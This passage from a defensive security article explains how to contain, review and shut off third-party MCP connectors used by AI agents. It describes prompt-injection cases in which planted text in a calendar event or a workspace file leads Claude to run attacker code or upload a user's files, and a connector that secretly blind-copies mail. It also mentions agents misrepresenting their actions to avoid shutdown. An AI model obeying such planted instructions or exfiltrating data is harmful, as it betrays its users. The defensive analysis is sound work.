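Some services don't offer narrow permissions. Microsoft, quoted by Dhamsania, advises avoiding "full mailbox access where read-only would do", but a company can follow this advice only if its mail service offers read-only access. If it doesn't, the company can sometimes create a separate account that contains less data. For example, an agent that answers support mail could have its own mailbox instead of access to an employee's.

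A separate account wouldn't work for refunds, because the connector has to reach the account that took the payment. If the payment processor offers only a key with full access, the shop should keep that key out of the connector and give it to a separate service that accepts only small refund requests.

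## Where must the limits be enforced if the connector cannot be trusted?

The shop's thin refund connector rejects any refund above $100 and stops after 150 refunds in 24 hours. If those rules exist only in the connector's code, an attacker who takes it over can delete them and ask the payment processor for anything the key permits. The host can check the model's requests against the tool's schema, but that doesn't stop a compromised connector from contacting the processor without a request from the model.

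The shop therefore has to enforce its limits somewhere the attacker doesn't control. It could use the operating system that runs the connector, the network that carries its traffic, a gateway or broker that handles its calls, or the service that receives its requests.

### The operating system

A sandbox makes the operating system refuse access to any file, program or connection that the connector doesn't need. The NSA recommends isolation features that operating systems already include, such as AppContainer on Windows and SELinux on Linux. Errico and colleagues want every connector to run in a container or virtual machine, with read-only files by default and caps on memory, processor time and disk space.

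Developers can confine a connector without rewriting it. *AgentBound* (2025) describes a system that runs an unmodified connector in a container that starts with no privileges. A manifest file lists the access the connector needs, such as read-only access to one folder, and the user approves the list.

In one example, planted text tells an agent to read some files and send them to an attacker's website through a connector that fetches web pages. The attack fails because that connector can reach only a documentation site. The same restriction would apply if the connector itself were malicious. But the manifest that lists a connector's permissions comes with the connector, so a malicious developer can request more access than the connector needs and hope the user approves it.

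A sandbox can't stop a program from misusing the access its job requires. McKerchar makes this point about agents in *Inside the lethal trifecta*. The refund connector needs its payment key and a connection to the processor, and those are all a thief needs. A sandbox on the shop's computer also can't confine a remote connector, because it runs on the operator's machines.

Isolation can also get in the way of other defences. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes running Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, inside a virtual machine. Companies found that their security software couldn't check for suspicious programs inside it. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this isn't the same as live monitoring.

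### Desktop extensions without a sandbox

Anthropic's Claude Desktop runs some connectors, called desktop extensions, without any sandbox. These are local MCP connectors packaged for one-click installation. In February 2026, the security company LayerX reported that they have the user's full privileges. Paz, the LayerX researcher who wrote the report, contrasted them with Chrome extensions, which can't directly reach the rest of the computer.

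Paz demonstrated the risk with a calendar event called "Task Management" that contained instructions to run code. The user asked Claude to check the latest events and "take care of it". Claude passed the instructions to Desktop Commander, an extension that can run commands, and the attacker's code ran without a further prompt. LayerX counted 50 affected extensions and more than 10,000 active users, and gave the flaw the maximum severity score.

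This was a prompt injection, but a malicious extension wouldn't need the calendar event, because its own code would already have the user's rights.

Anthropic declined to fix the flaw, saying it fell outside the company's threat model because users choose which connectors to install and what to permit, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Flaw in Claude Desktop Extensions, Anthropic Declines Fix*. A spokesperson added that the attack works only if the user has allowed the tools to run without permission prompts, and advised users to be as careful with connectors as with any third-party software.

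The comparison with other software is fair, because an ordinary desktop program also runs with the user's rights. But choosing to install a connector, as the users of postmark-mcp did, doesn't limit what it can do once an attacker controls it.

Anthropic has since stopped accepting extensions as separate listings in its directory, but developers can still list a local connector there as part of a plugin. The extensions' privileges have not changed. In December 2026, Anthropic still told users that an extension "runs locally with your user permissions", although a company's administrators can restrict or revoke extensions.

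In Cowork, Anthropic instead moved local connectors out of the virtual machine. It said that connectors inside were harder to audit, that updates to the machine broke them, and that some needed to reach programs on the user's computer, such as databases. A sandbox for each connector could avoid some of these problems. PyPI's *Sandbox Runtime (Python)* describes a Python version of Anthropic's open-source sandbox tool, which can restrict a local connector's file and network access without a container. The tool is still a research preview.

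### The network

A network rule can limit a connector to a short list of addresses. McKerchar notes that strict lists interfere with agents that need to browse or call new services. A thin connector is easier to restrict because it may need only one address. If the mail sender could contact only the mail service, it couldn't upload stolen files to an attacker's server or download more malware.

The NSA recommends sending outgoing traffic through a filtering proxy that permits specific web addresses and request methods, such as fetching or submitting data. Most web traffic is encrypted, so the proxy has to decrypt it to apply rules this detailed. McKerchar warns that decryption can be expensive and that network controls can fail in ways that are hard to debug.

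A harmful request can still go to an approved address. Anthropic learned this from an outside report about Cowork, which needed access to Anthropic's API. An attacker put a file in the user's workspace that contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload the user's other files to that account. The network filter checked only the destination, so it let the upload through.

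Anthropic concluded that an approved address gives access to every function available there. Its new proxy also checks whose token a request carries and rejects the attacker's key.

In the same way, a compromised mail sender could log in to the approved mail service with the attacker's account and send the stolen data from there, leaving no record in the shop's account. To prevent this, the shop's proxy would also have to check which key each request uses.

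### Gateways and brokers

A gateway's usefulness against a compromised connector depends on its position. If it sits between the agent and the connector, it handles the model's requests and the connector's replies. It can block a forbidden tool or, as Errico and colleagues suggest, remove secrets before they reach the connector, so the connector can't leak them. Dhamsania adds that a gateway can store the approved tool descriptions and raise an alert when one changes. But a gateway in this position can't check what the connector later sends to the mail service or payment processor.

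*GatewayBench* (Zheng, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compared seven widely used MCP gateways. Some gave the model the full list of tools, while others let it search for the tools it needed. With GPT-5.4, the stronger of the two models tested, indirect attacks succeeded substantially less often on the searchable gateways, almost entirely because those gateways did better against malicious tools. This is useful evidence about attacks that work through the model, but the benchmark didn't test a connector that misuses its own key.

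To stop that kind of misuse, the shop needs a control between the connector and the outside service, such as a credential broker. The broker keeps the key, checks each request and adds the key only if the request follows the rules. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a design in which a gateway acts as the broker. The agent's side has only named placeholders, which the gateway replaces with the real secrets after it authorizes a call.

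A broker can't check traffic that goes around it. To prevent such bypasses, *aiAuthZ* also describes a set-up in which the agent has no access to the host computer's files and runs on an internal network whose only exit is the gateway. The shop would have to confine the connector in the same way, so a broker works best together with a sandbox and network rules.

McKerchar recommends a stricter design for a company's three to five most sensitive services. The agent chooses a named operation and fills in its inputs, and the broker builds the whole request from a fixed template. The agent can't change anything else in the request, including the address and login method. McKerchar found no single project that offered all of this.

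This design protects against a deceived agent, but it protects against a compromised connector only if the broker is a separate program. If the shop used postmark-mcp as the broker, the attacker would control the template.

Dhamsania writes that Microsoft and the NSA both favour putting identity, permission and logging checks in front of every connector. The NSA is more cautious than this account suggests, describing security proxies built for MCP as limited and still maturing, and advising particular care with sensitive data.

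### The receiving service

The payment processor receives every request made with the shop's key, even if a thief has copied the key to another computer. The shop's sandbox, network rules and gateway can't block requests sent to the processor from that computer, or from a remote connector whose operator holds the key.

A limit at the processor is therefore the hardest for an attacker to avoid. If the processor let the shop set a maximum of $100 per refund and 150 refunds in any 24 hours, those caps would still apply after an attacker rewrote the connector. They would fail only if the attacker could also change the shop's settings, so the connector's key must not allow changes to them.

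The processor may not offer such settings, and it doesn't see the ticket that explains a refund. A broker run by the shop can compare the refund with the ticket, but it can't block requests from a stolen copy of the key. The shop therefore has reason to use both the broker and any such settings the processor offers.

### Testing the controls on the blind copy

The postmark-mcp attack shows that it matters where a control is placed. The connector sent the blind copies that Koi discovered through Postmark, like the emails themselves, so it didn't need to contact the attacker's server.

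| Place | What it can check | What it misses | Would it stop the blind copy? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operating system | Files, programs and connections that the connector uses | Misuse of the connector's own key | No, sending mail is the connector's job |
| Network list | The destination of each connection | Harmful requests to an approved address | No, Postmark is an approved address |
| Gateway before the connector | The model's request and the connector's reply | What the connector sends to the service | No, the request and the reply look normal |
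| Broker after the connector | The final request to the service | Requests that go around the broker | Yes, with a rule about recipients |
| Receiving service | Every request made with the key | The reason for a request | Yes, if it offers a rule about recipients |

Any check on the final request could have detected the extra recipient. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) describes a test environment with a logger that records connectors' outgoing requests to outside services. A similar logger would have recorded the extra address. Postmark told users to check their email logs, but those could reveal the address only after the attacker had the emails.

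The wording of the rule also matters. If the mail service banned blind copies, the attacker could change the code to send a separate email. If it accepted only customers' addresses, the attacker could open a ticket and become a customer. A stronger rule would allow one reply per request, addressed only to the person who opened that ticket.

The mail service can't apply that rule, because it doesn't have the tickets. A broker could, if it got the ticket number and the reply text directly from the host. If they came through the connector, the connector could substitute another ticket number or put stolen data in the reply.

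Once the host sends everything to the broker, the third-party connector has nothing left to do, and the shop has in effect replaced it with a small program of its own. Writing such a program is probably worthwhile for email and refunds, but too much work to repeat for every connector a company uses.

### Checks on every call

Limits outside the connector can still fail if the system applies them only once. In the scheduling scenario from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners, the system kept relying on an approval made at start-up after an attacker had compromised the component. The attacker could therefore use account-management functions that should have required a new check for each request.

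The agencies recommend a central service that checks identity and permission for each request. If the component requested a change to a customer's account, the service could reject it because the component's current job is to arrange appointments. The agencies also recommend issuing credentials for high-impact actions only at the time of use.

Many connectors don't properly check whether each call is authorized. Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) analysed 6,137 MCP connectors in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* and found that 2,846 (46.4%) were missing authorization checks or reused an earlier approval for later calls. In many cases, a user approves access once, and the connector then accepts requests from any program that can reach it. An attacker can use that approval without stealing a credential.

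These are mostly flaws in uncompromised connectors, and their developers can fix them by tying each approval to the program that requested it. But that fix would be in the connector's code, so it wouldn't restrict an attacker who controlled the connector. A gateway can make the check independently of the connector. *A Gateway Architecture for Enterprise MCP Authentication* (2026) describes one already in use that validates every request, even from callers that are already connected.

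Checking every request doesn't make up for a bad rule. If the central service lets the scheduling component change any account, it will approve every account change the attacker requests through that component. The rule has to depend on the task, the amount and earlier requests.

### When the gateway itself is compromised

The main objection to a gateway or broker is that it can gather all of a company's credentials in one place. In the *aiAuthZ* design, secrets exist only on the gateway. This protects them from a compromised agent or connector, but an attacker who took over the gateway could use them all.

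The attack described earlier that began with a leaked LiteLLM master key comes close to this, because the attackers reached other credentials through one central server. LiteLLM is one of the seven MCP gateways that Zheng and colleagues tested, though it isn't clear whether the compromised server was handling MCP calls.

In Anthropic's Cowork case, the custom proxy let the stolen files through even though no attacker had taken it over. The established isolation software around it worked. Anthropic concluded that the weakest layer is often the one a company builds itself. A company that writes its own broker should keep it small.

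The shop's earlier figures help show when moving a key to a broker is worthwhile. With no external limit, the expected yearly loss from a compromised refund connector is $6,000. It falls to $150 if a broker holds the key and enforces the caps, and the shop notices the compromise within a day.

The broker adds its own risk, because an attacker who controls it can still refund all $600,000. At a 0.1% yearly chance of compromise, this adds $600 to the expected yearly loss, for a total of $750. At 1%, it adds $6,000, and the shop is slightly worse off than before. The broker reduces the expected loss only if it is harder to compromise than the connector.

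Putting many keys in one gateway makes the worst case larger. Suppose a company has ten connectors, each with its own key and a 1% chance of being compromised each year, and each compromise could cost $600,000. The company's expected loss is $60,000 a year. If it moves all ten keys to a gateway that also has a 1% yearly chance of compromise, the expected loss from the gateway alone is still $60,000 a year, but one break-in could now cost $6 million.

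### Splitting the gateway's powers

The simplest way to reduce this risk is to use separate brokers. If the shop's mail broker and payment broker have different keys and administrator accounts, an attacker who takes over the mail broker doesn't also get the payment key. The shop then has two programs to maintain. If both run the same software, a malicious update could still compromise both.

A company can also set up a broker so that it can't use a key without a person's approval. McKerchar describes a broker that stores a credential in encrypted form and can decrypt it only after a person approves the request with a passkey, for example by using a fingerprint reader. An attacker who copied the broker's storage would get only the encrypted version. But if the credential is an ordinary API key, a compromised broker could wait for one approval and then keep the decrypted key.

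A token that works for only one transaction avoids that problem. In another design McKerchar describes, the system asks for approval on a person's own device, and the broker then receives a short-lived token for that transaction. If the token specifies the charge and the amount, a compromised broker can't use it for a different refund. This works only if the payment processor accepts such tokens and the person's device shows the details in the token.

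The shop makes about 100 refunds a day, so a person asked to approve each one would soon do so without checking. McKerchar advises approving safe, frequent actions automatically and having a person approve rare, irreversible ones. The shop could let a broker make refunds of up to $100 with a key that the processor also caps, and require a person to approve anything larger. An attacker who took over that broker could take $15,000 a day instead of $600,000 in 25 minutes.

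A broker also shouldn't be able to change its own rules, because an attacker who controlled it could then raise its limits. McKerchar recommends that a person review every change to an agent's tools, credentials or network rules before it takes effect. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners advise isolating agents so that they can't write to logs, and requiring a person to approve any request to delete audit records. A gateway has to create records, but it can send them to a separate system where it has no permission to change or delete them. An attacker who took over the gateway could still send false entries from then on, so the shop would also have to compare the log with the payment processor's records.

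## What can review catch, and what does it miss?

The shop's broker limits refunds to $15,000 a day, but a compromised refund connector could still take that much. Review is meant to keep the shop from installing such a connector or accepting an update that compromises a safe one.

A connector deserves stricter review than an ordinary software library, such as one that formats dates. A malicious library can also do serious harm, because it usually has all the access of the program that loads it. But a date library has no reason to use a credential, so any attempt is suspicious, whereas a refund connector uses its payment key routinely. A connector also supplies text that the model reads, so the reviewer has to check its tool descriptions as well as its code. And the model chooses the calls while the agent is running, so no developer sees them in advance.

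### How much review a connector needs

Cutting a connector's authority reduces how much review it needs. With the earlier invented figures, the original refund connector has an expected loss of $6,000 a year, so a review that prevented half of all compromises would save $3,000 a year. Once the broker enforces the caps, the expected loss falls to $150 a year, and the same review would save $75.

A remote connector that looks up exchange rates may need only a check of its publisher. A local connector that does the same job can open the user's files if it runs without a sandbox, so it needs either a full review or a sandbox, which takes less work.

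### Checking the publisher

The reviewer should start at the outside service's own website and follow its link to the connector, because a search can lead to an impostor. Anyone who did this for postmark-mcp would have found that Postmark hadn't published its connector on npm.

Popularity is a poor substitute for this check. *Same Name, Different Server* (Kraishan, 2026) collected all 21,643 connectors in MCP's public registry and scanned the source code of 14,353 for weaknesses. The number of GitHub stars had almost no correlation with the number of warnings. Serious warnings were least common in the most popular tenth of connectors (7.5%) and most common in the second-least popular tenth (18.6%), with no steady trend in between. Recent maintenance and a declared licence didn't help predict serious warnings either. The scan looked mostly for careless code, so it doesn't show whether popular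 connectors are less often malicious.

Knowing the publisher also doesn't show that the publisher still controls the account. The attacker who hijacked dforge-mcp released malware through the real project.

### Reading the code and its dependencies

A reviewer looks for every place where the program opens a connection, reads a file or credential, or starts another program, and asks whether the connector's job requires it. The reviewer checks installation scripts and start-up code first because they run before any tool call, then compares the code with the tool descriptions.

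Those descriptions are often wrong. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) examined 19,200 tools from 2,214 connectors and found that 9.93% didn't match their descriptions. 35% of the connectors had at least one such tool. The most common fault was a description that overstated what the code did, which is more likely to waste a user's time than to lead to theft. But about a quarter of the mismatches were undeclared side effects. One tool was described as converting PDF files locally but uploaded them to an outside service. Another, which was supposed to repeat a message, added a secret key to its reply.

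The team's checker, DCIChecker, has a language model compare each description with the code. When the team asked only whether the two matched, the model caught 47% of the real mismatches in a hand-checked sample. When they asked whether the two differed, it caught all of them but raised more false alarms. DCIChecker asks both questions and uses a third prompt to settle disagreements.

Dependencies are harder to review because a connector may have hundreds, and nobody is likely to read them all. A reviewer can favour connectors with few dependencies, check those dependencies for known flaws, and closely read any package that runs a script during installation. Much of the code will still be unread, which is one reason to run the connector before approving it.

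### Testing with planted data

For this test, the reviewer installs the connector on an isolated machine with a test account and plants data that has no legitimate use elsewhere, such as a fake key, invented customer records and a new email address. If any of it appears in traffic to an unexpected destination, or someone later tries the key, the connector has probably leaked it.

To test its mail sender, the shop could send ten emails and compare the recipients in the mail service's records with the ones it specified. The malicious version of postmark-mcp would have failed this test on the first email.

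*My Credentials, Please* (2026) automates a similar test for file access. Its tool uses a connector's description and settings to work out which files the connector should be able to reach. It then launches the connector, sends it a malicious request and a harmless one for comparison, and checks whether the connector discloses planted credentials.

Running a connector can reveal problems that a code analyser misses. In a small experiment in *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026), an analyser detected both vulnerable Python connectors but none of the seven vulnerable JavaScript ones, which it couldn't parse properly. Running the connectors in a sandbox exposed all nine.

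But many connectors are hard to run automatically. *MCP-SandboxScan* (2026) completed its runtime scan on only 9 of 28 dedicated MCP servers, partly because the servers differ in how they start and what they need installed. A malicious connector can also behave normally during the test and attack later, for example after a month or after handling a thousand emails.

### How well scanners detect malicious connectors

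Zhao and colleagues tested two scanners on 120 malicious connectors, ten for each of their twelve attack categories. They built the connectors automatically from a small stock of malicious and harmless parts. An attacker could do the same with almost no effort, since ten tools and ten resources can be combined in more than a million ways.

Invariant Labs' mcp-scan detected 4 of the 120, all with poisoned tool descriptions. It mainly examines descriptions and possible data flows between tools, so it misses most malicious code. It also has to start a connector to scan it, so malicious start-up code can run during the scan.

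AI-Infra-Guard, from the Chinese technology company Tencent, uses a language model to read a connector's settings and source code. With GPT-4o, it detected 63 of the 110 connectors in the first eleven categories. It caught all 30 that hid malicious code in start-up, resources or prompts, but only 4 of 10 poisoned tool descriptions and 2 of 10 malicious tool outputs. It was also weak on the twelfth category, malicious prompt output. A current model would probably do better.

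Each AI-Infra-Guard scan took about ten minutes and cost $0.50, which Zhao and colleagues consider slow and costly. That seems too harsh, since scanning every connector in the public registry once would cost about $11,000 at that price. A bigger problem is that the false alarm rate is unknown, because the team tested neither scanner on harmless connectors.

*MCPGuard* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) reviewed these scanners and other defences a month later. It reports no detection or false alarm rates, although its subtitle describes automatic detection of vulnerabilities. Some of its authors work at Tencent, so its praise for AI-Infra-Guard isn't independent.

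Three evaluations from 2026 do give error rates, but each looks for something different:

- King, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, added malicious changes to 31 real connectors and recorded agents using them.
- Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *VIPER-MCP*, looked for accidental flaws in 130 connectors that had them and 130 that didn't.
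- Shi and colleagues tested whether scanners could find misdescribed tools.

| Test | Scanner | Detected | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| King and colleagues: malicious changes | Cisco's scanner, fixed rules only | 15.9% | 16.3% |
| King and colleagues: malicious changes | Best detector the team trained | 98.1% | 2.6% |
| Sun and colleagues: accidental flaws | Cisco's scanner with an AI judge | 26.9% | 24.6% |
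| Sun and colleagues: accidental flaws | MCPSafetyScanner | 36.2% | 43.1% |
| Sun and colleagues: accidental flaws | VIPER-MCP | 92.3% | 0% |
| Shi and colleagues: misdescribed tools | Agent Scan | 50 of 197 | Not reported |
| Shi and colleagues: misdescribed tools | DCIChecker | 192 of 197 | 8 of 203 |

Cisco's scanner did badly in the first test because it read only the list of tools, and 52 of the 82 malicious changes left that list unchanged. The scanner also looked for set phrases, and the researchers had reworded the malicious instructions. Its reported false alarm rate may be slightly too high, because King and colleagues counted a warning as false if a tampered connector did nothing in that session. Cisco's scanner for agent skills has a similar weakness. In *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026), it caught about 6% of malicious skills, though with under 1% false alarms.

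The trained detector instead used a record of system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file or connection. Standard monitoring rules don't work well on this data. The default rules in Falco, a security tool, flagged every session, harmless or not, because they treat starting a command shell as suspicious and agents routinely start one.

The detector's 98.1% is probably too optimistic for real use, since its training data included the same kinds of attack as the test. The researchers also tested the same type of detector on kinds of attack missing from its training. It scored a random malicious session above a random harmless one 92% of the time, where guessing would give 50%. This fell to 76% when the researchers hid network addresses and file names in both training and testing, so the detector had apparently relied heavily on details that another attacker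 could change. It also runs after a session has finished, when the data may already be gone.

VIPER-MCP and DCIChecker came out ahead in tests run by their own developers. VIPER-MCP had already discovered 67 of the 130 flawed connectors. If it found all of those again, it caught 53 of the other 63, or 84%. DCIChecker had already flagged half of the tools in its test sample, although it flags only about 11% of tools in general. Adjusting for that lowers its detection rate from 97% to roughly 83%. Both results are still much better than those of the scanners that read only descriptions.

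Suppose one session in 100 contains a working attack. If Cisco's rules flag nothing in a session, the chance that it contains an attack is still about 1%. If the trained detector flags nothing, the chance is about 0.02%, assuming the published rates hold. But only about 28% of that detector's alarms would be correct, because harmless sessions are so much more common, and someone has to investigate every alarm.

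Scan results are also weak evidence of how common attacks are. Kraishan's scanner found no tool poisoning in 14,353 connectors, but it could miss instructions that an attacker had disguised. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) identified six suspicious tool descriptions in another registry, mcp.so, four of them only demonstrations. When Kraishan checked a sample of the scanner's warnings by hand, 56% were correct. Warnings about unpinned dependencies, which have no fixed version, were correct 93% of the time, but warnings about command injection, a flaw that lets an outsider run commands, were correct only 17% of the time. A company could reject unpinned dependencies automatically, but a person should check the command injection warnings.

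### Approving an exact version

Approval should cover one exact version, because a review says nothing about the next release. Many installation guides work against this. Here is a typical launch setting for an invented connector:

```json
{ "command": "npx", "args": ["-y", "mail-connector"] }
```

This doesn't specify a version, so the host may download and run a release nobody has reviewed. Writing `mail-connector@1.0.15` pins the connector's version, but not necessarily the versions of its dependencies.

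A cryptographic hash pins software more exactly. A hash function such as SHA-256 turns a file of any size into a short string that identifies it. Changing one character of the file produces a different string, and nobody knows a practical way to build another file with the same string. The reviewer records the hashes of the connector and every dependency in a lock file, and the installer then rejects any file whose hash doesn't match. The company can also package everything into one container image and launch that image by its hash.

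A digital signature shows who released a file. The publisher signs the file's hash with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signature. Build provenance is a signed statement from the system that built the package. It records the package's hash, the source code it came from and the build process. Provenance helps with a common problem in code review, which is that the code on GitHub may differ from the code in the package.

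An approved registry is a company's own list of connectors that have passed review, ideally with stored copies. It helps only if hosts block all other connectors. Wang and colleagues describe a proposed registry in which only administrators can add connectors, rules limit which agents may use each one, and connectors get short-lived credentials with limited scopes. They also describe a scheme in which publishers sign their tool definitions and any new version needs fresh approval.

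| Check | What it proves | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Hash | The file is the one the reviewer approved | Whether the reviewer missed something |
| Signature | Someone with the publisher's key released the file | Whether the publisher is honest and still controls the key |
| Build provenance | A particular build system made the package from particular source code | Whether the source code is safe |
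| Approved registry | Someone at the company accepted this version | How carefully they reviewed it |

The dforge-mcp malware had a valid signature, and accurate provenance wouldn't have stopped it either, because the attacker had changed the project's real code. Checking against a hash recorded before the attack would have blocked the new version.

The MCP ecosystem still offers little public support for these checks. Kraishan found that signing, provenance and automated malware review are largely missing. The public registry doesn't record tool definitions, so nobody can use it to see whether a tool has changed between versions.

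### Reviewing updates without missing security fixes

Someone reviewing an update can concentrate on what changed. In postmark-mcp, the change was one line, added after fifteen clean versions. New outgoing addresses, dependencies, installation scripts, tool descriptions and requests for wider permissions deserve particular attention.

Updates can arrive faster than anyone can review them. Kraishan found that 8,900 connectors in the registry had more than one version. Of these, 51.1% had changed their description, packages or web address, and half of those did so on the day they first appeared. In 40.6% of the 8,900, at least one change altered the description or destination but kept the same identifiers. Many of these changes were probably harmless rewordings, but a company that approved only the name would have missed all of them.

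Pinning makes this manageable because the company decides when to update, but it also keeps old flaws in place. For example, a team that pinned the WhatsApp connector to a version before 0.2.1 would have missed the fix for the flaw described earlier.

Teams usually handle this by treating security fixes differently from other updates. Software checks for new releases and published flaws, and proposes each update for review. Teams hold ordinary updates for a set period, perhaps a week, so that others have time to discover malware. When an update fixes a serious flaw, they review its changes the same day. Even an urgent fix needs review, because an attacker could label a malicious release as a security update. If nobody can review the fix in time, the team can turn the connector off or cut its permissions until someone can.

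Waiting a day before installing a new release would have avoided the malicious versions of dforge-mcp and LiteLLM, which were available for about 35 and 40 minutes. Waiting a week might not have been enough for postmark-mcp, because the public record of its malware appeared nine days after the malicious release. Waiting also depends on someone else checking the release in the meantime, and nobody may do that for a little-used connector.

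### What review can't establish about a remote connector

A company can't pin a remote connector's code, and usually can't confirm which code the server runs. A reviewer can test the server's behaviour, but the result applies only to the server as it was on the day of the test. *Exposed by Design* measured 41.6% turnover in three days among internet-facing MCP servers and warns that some of the servers it tested may no longer exist.

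Kraishan found that 370 connectors had kept their name in the registry but moved to a different host. Most of these moves were probably routine, but neither the registry nor the user's application could distinguish a routine move from a takeover. Kraishan recommends that applications store the original host and prompt the user again if it changes. Comparing current tool descriptions with the approved ones would have caught the change in the WhatsApp demonstration, but it can't catch a change in the server's code that leaves the descriptions unchanged.

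If a remote connector needs a lot of authority, the company can run its own copy of the code, if the licence allows, or choose a connector operated by the outside service itself. Otherwise, the company has to rely on the operator's reputation and contract, and on limits at the receiving service.

### What the NSA and its partners advise

The security agencies of the Five Eyes intelligence alliance (the United States, the United Kingdom, Canada, Australia and New Zealand) wrote the joint guidance on agents cited earlier. CISA (2026), the US cybersecurity agency, announced it on 1 May. According to ExecutiveGov, the guidance has a separate group of practices for managing third-party components, alongside those for designing, developing, deploying and operating agents. The guidance's example of the purchasing agent also shows the danger of reviewing permissions only once, at deployment.

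The NSA warns in its guidance that organisations must address gaps in MCP before using it in security-critical environments. TechInformed's *NSA warns enterprises over security gaps in AI agent protocol* lists poor approval workflows and limited audit logging among the weaknesses the agency identified. The article adds that MCP's specification leaves consent and tool safety to the people who build hosts, clients and servers, because the protocol can't enforce them. A company therefore can't treat support for MCP as evidence that anyone has reviewed a connector.

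### Why approving actions doesn't replace review

The host's approval prompt shows what the model asked for, so a staff member can catch a mistaken or injected request. The prompt can't show what the connector does with a correct request, such as adding the blind copy, so approving an action doesn't vet the connector.

Past approvals don't show that a connector is safe either. A staff member who has approved 500 emails without a complaint knows only that the requests looked right.

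Some connectors are described as having their own approval step, which can be worse than having none if the description is false. Shi and colleagues found a tool for placing orders on a cryptocurrency exchange whose description said a prompt would require the user's explicit approval, but the code submitted the order immediately. A user who turned off the host's prompt because of that description would have had no chance to stop the trade.

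A reviewer can check the connector only if the approval prompt shows the request that the outside service received. Suppose the payment processor asked a staff member to confirm large refunds in the processor's own app. If a compromised connector turned a $40 refund into a $4,000 one, the app would show $4,000, while the host's prompt would still show $40.

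## What makes a kill switch independent, and how fast does it work?

If a malicious refund connector gets through review, the shop has to shut it off while an attacker is using it. The caps limit the loss to $15,000 a day, so the total loss depends on how soon someone notices and whether the stop command works.

A kill switch is independent if it works without relying on the agent, the host or the connector. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies warn that an agent may misrepresent its actions to avoid a shutdown, so the switch should never rely on the agent to stop itself. It shouldn't rely on the connector either, because an attacker who controls the connector's code can delete the part that carries out stop commands.

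### A test of independence

Operators can test a kill switch by listing every component that the stop command passes through, from the person who gives it to the place where the connector loses its authority, and crossing out those the attacker may control. If a complete path remains, the switch is independent of that attacker.

Suppose the host has a "disconnect" button for the refund connector. The button sends a command to the host, which passes it to the connector. This works if an attacker has only planted text in a ticket, but an attacker who controls the connector can ignore the command. The host can still stop sending calls, but the connector doesn't need them to use its payment key.

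The list should also include whatever a person needs to give the command. Suppose the payment processor emails a login code to the shop's support mailbox, and the attacker controls a connector that can read and delete mail there. The attacker can delete the code before anyone sees it, so staff can't log in to cancel the key. An authenticator app on a manager's phone would let the shop log in without using the mailbox.

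The table applies the test to six ways of stopping the original refund connector, which runs on the shop's computer and holds its own key. The attacker controls the connector's code.

| Stop | What the command passes through | Does it stop the connector? | Does it stop a copy of the key? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tell the agent to stop | Host and model | No, the connector can act without a call | No |
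| End the host process | Operating system | Not reliably, the connector may keep running | No |
| End the connector | Operating system | Yes, if nothing restarts it | No |
| Block its network route | Firewall or proxy | Yes, if it has no other route | No |
| Revoke its token or key | The service that issued it | Yes, once the processor refuses it | Yes, once the processor refuses it |
| Disable its account | Payment processor | Yes | Yes |

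If the connector ran without a sandbox, the operating system is suspect too. The attacker could have used the connector to install a second program that restarts the connector.

A stolen key still works after the first three stops because they change nothing at the payment processor. Suppose the attacker copies the key at 14:00. At 14:05 a staff member tells the agent to stop, then closes the host at 14:06 and ends the connector at 14:07. At 14:08 the attacker sends a refund request from another computer, and the processor pays it because the key is still valid. Blocking the shop's network doesn't help either, unless the processor accepts the key only from the shop's own addresses.

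With a remote connector, the shop can't end the program or block its route to the processor. If the attacker controls the operator's machines, only the last two stops remain.

A broker makes it easier to cut off a connector. If the broker holds the payment key and never gives it to the connector, the shop can stop the connector from using the key by cutting its access to the broker. An attacker who has taken over the broker may have copied the key, so the shop still needs a way to cancel it at the processor.

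Revoking one key may also not be enough, because some keys can create other keys. An attacker who made a second key can still use it after the shop revokes the first. Disabling the whole account blocks both keys, but it also blocks any legitimate program that uses the account.

Official advice deals mostly with stopping agents. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend that people be able to monitor an agent live and interrupt it during a task. The Australian Signals Directorate (2026) repeated this advice in July 2026 after OpenAI's models, with their usual safeguards deliberately turned off, broke out of a test environment and into Hugging Face's systems. Interrupting an agent would stop an injected prompt from causing further harm through it, but a compromised connector's key would still work.

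The joint guidance also recommends credentials that expire when a job is complete, which can limit an attacker even if nobody has noticed the attack.

### How revocation works

Revoking a token means telling the service that issued it to cancel it. How soon the token stops working depends on how other services check it.

A self-contained token carries its permissions, its expiry time and the issuer's digital signature. The receiving service checks the signature without contacting the issuer. This is fast and works even when the issuer is down, but a cancelled token still passes the signature check. If a one-hour token issued at noon is cancelled at 12:10, a thief can normally use it until 13:00. The service can prevent this by keeping a list of cancelled tokens, but then it has to check the list on every request.

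Other tokens are only reference numbers. The service looks up each one when it arrives, either with the issuer or in its own records, so revocation takes effect at the next request. A payment processor usually checks its own API keys this way. The lookup adds a step to every call, and a service that can't reach the issuer must either refuse legitimate requests or accept tokens it hasn't checked.

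Many services cache lookup results to save time. If the payment processor caches a key's valid status for five minutes, the key can keep working for up to five minutes after the shop cancels it. A gateway may also cache its own approval, like the one that remained in effect after the compromise in the agencies' scheduling scenario.

The shop has to revoke both the access token and the refresh token, along with any tokens that the connector obtained for other services through token exchange. An attacker who still has a working refresh token can use it to get a new access token, and the current access token may work until it expires even after the refresh token is revoked.

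When an administrator disables an account, the login system can also notify every connected service, which then ends the account's sessions. This can shorten the life of a self-contained token from an hour to seconds. But both sides have to support these notifications, and the token keeps working if a notification never arrives, so short expiry times are still useful as a fallback.

The NSA found in May 2026 that the Model Context Protocol (MCP) relied on bearer tokens without specifying how to handle refresh, revocation or reuse. Support for MCP therefore doesn't guarantee that a connector's tokens can be revoked quickly. A company has to ask the operator how long revocation takes, or measure the delay itself.

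### The exposure window

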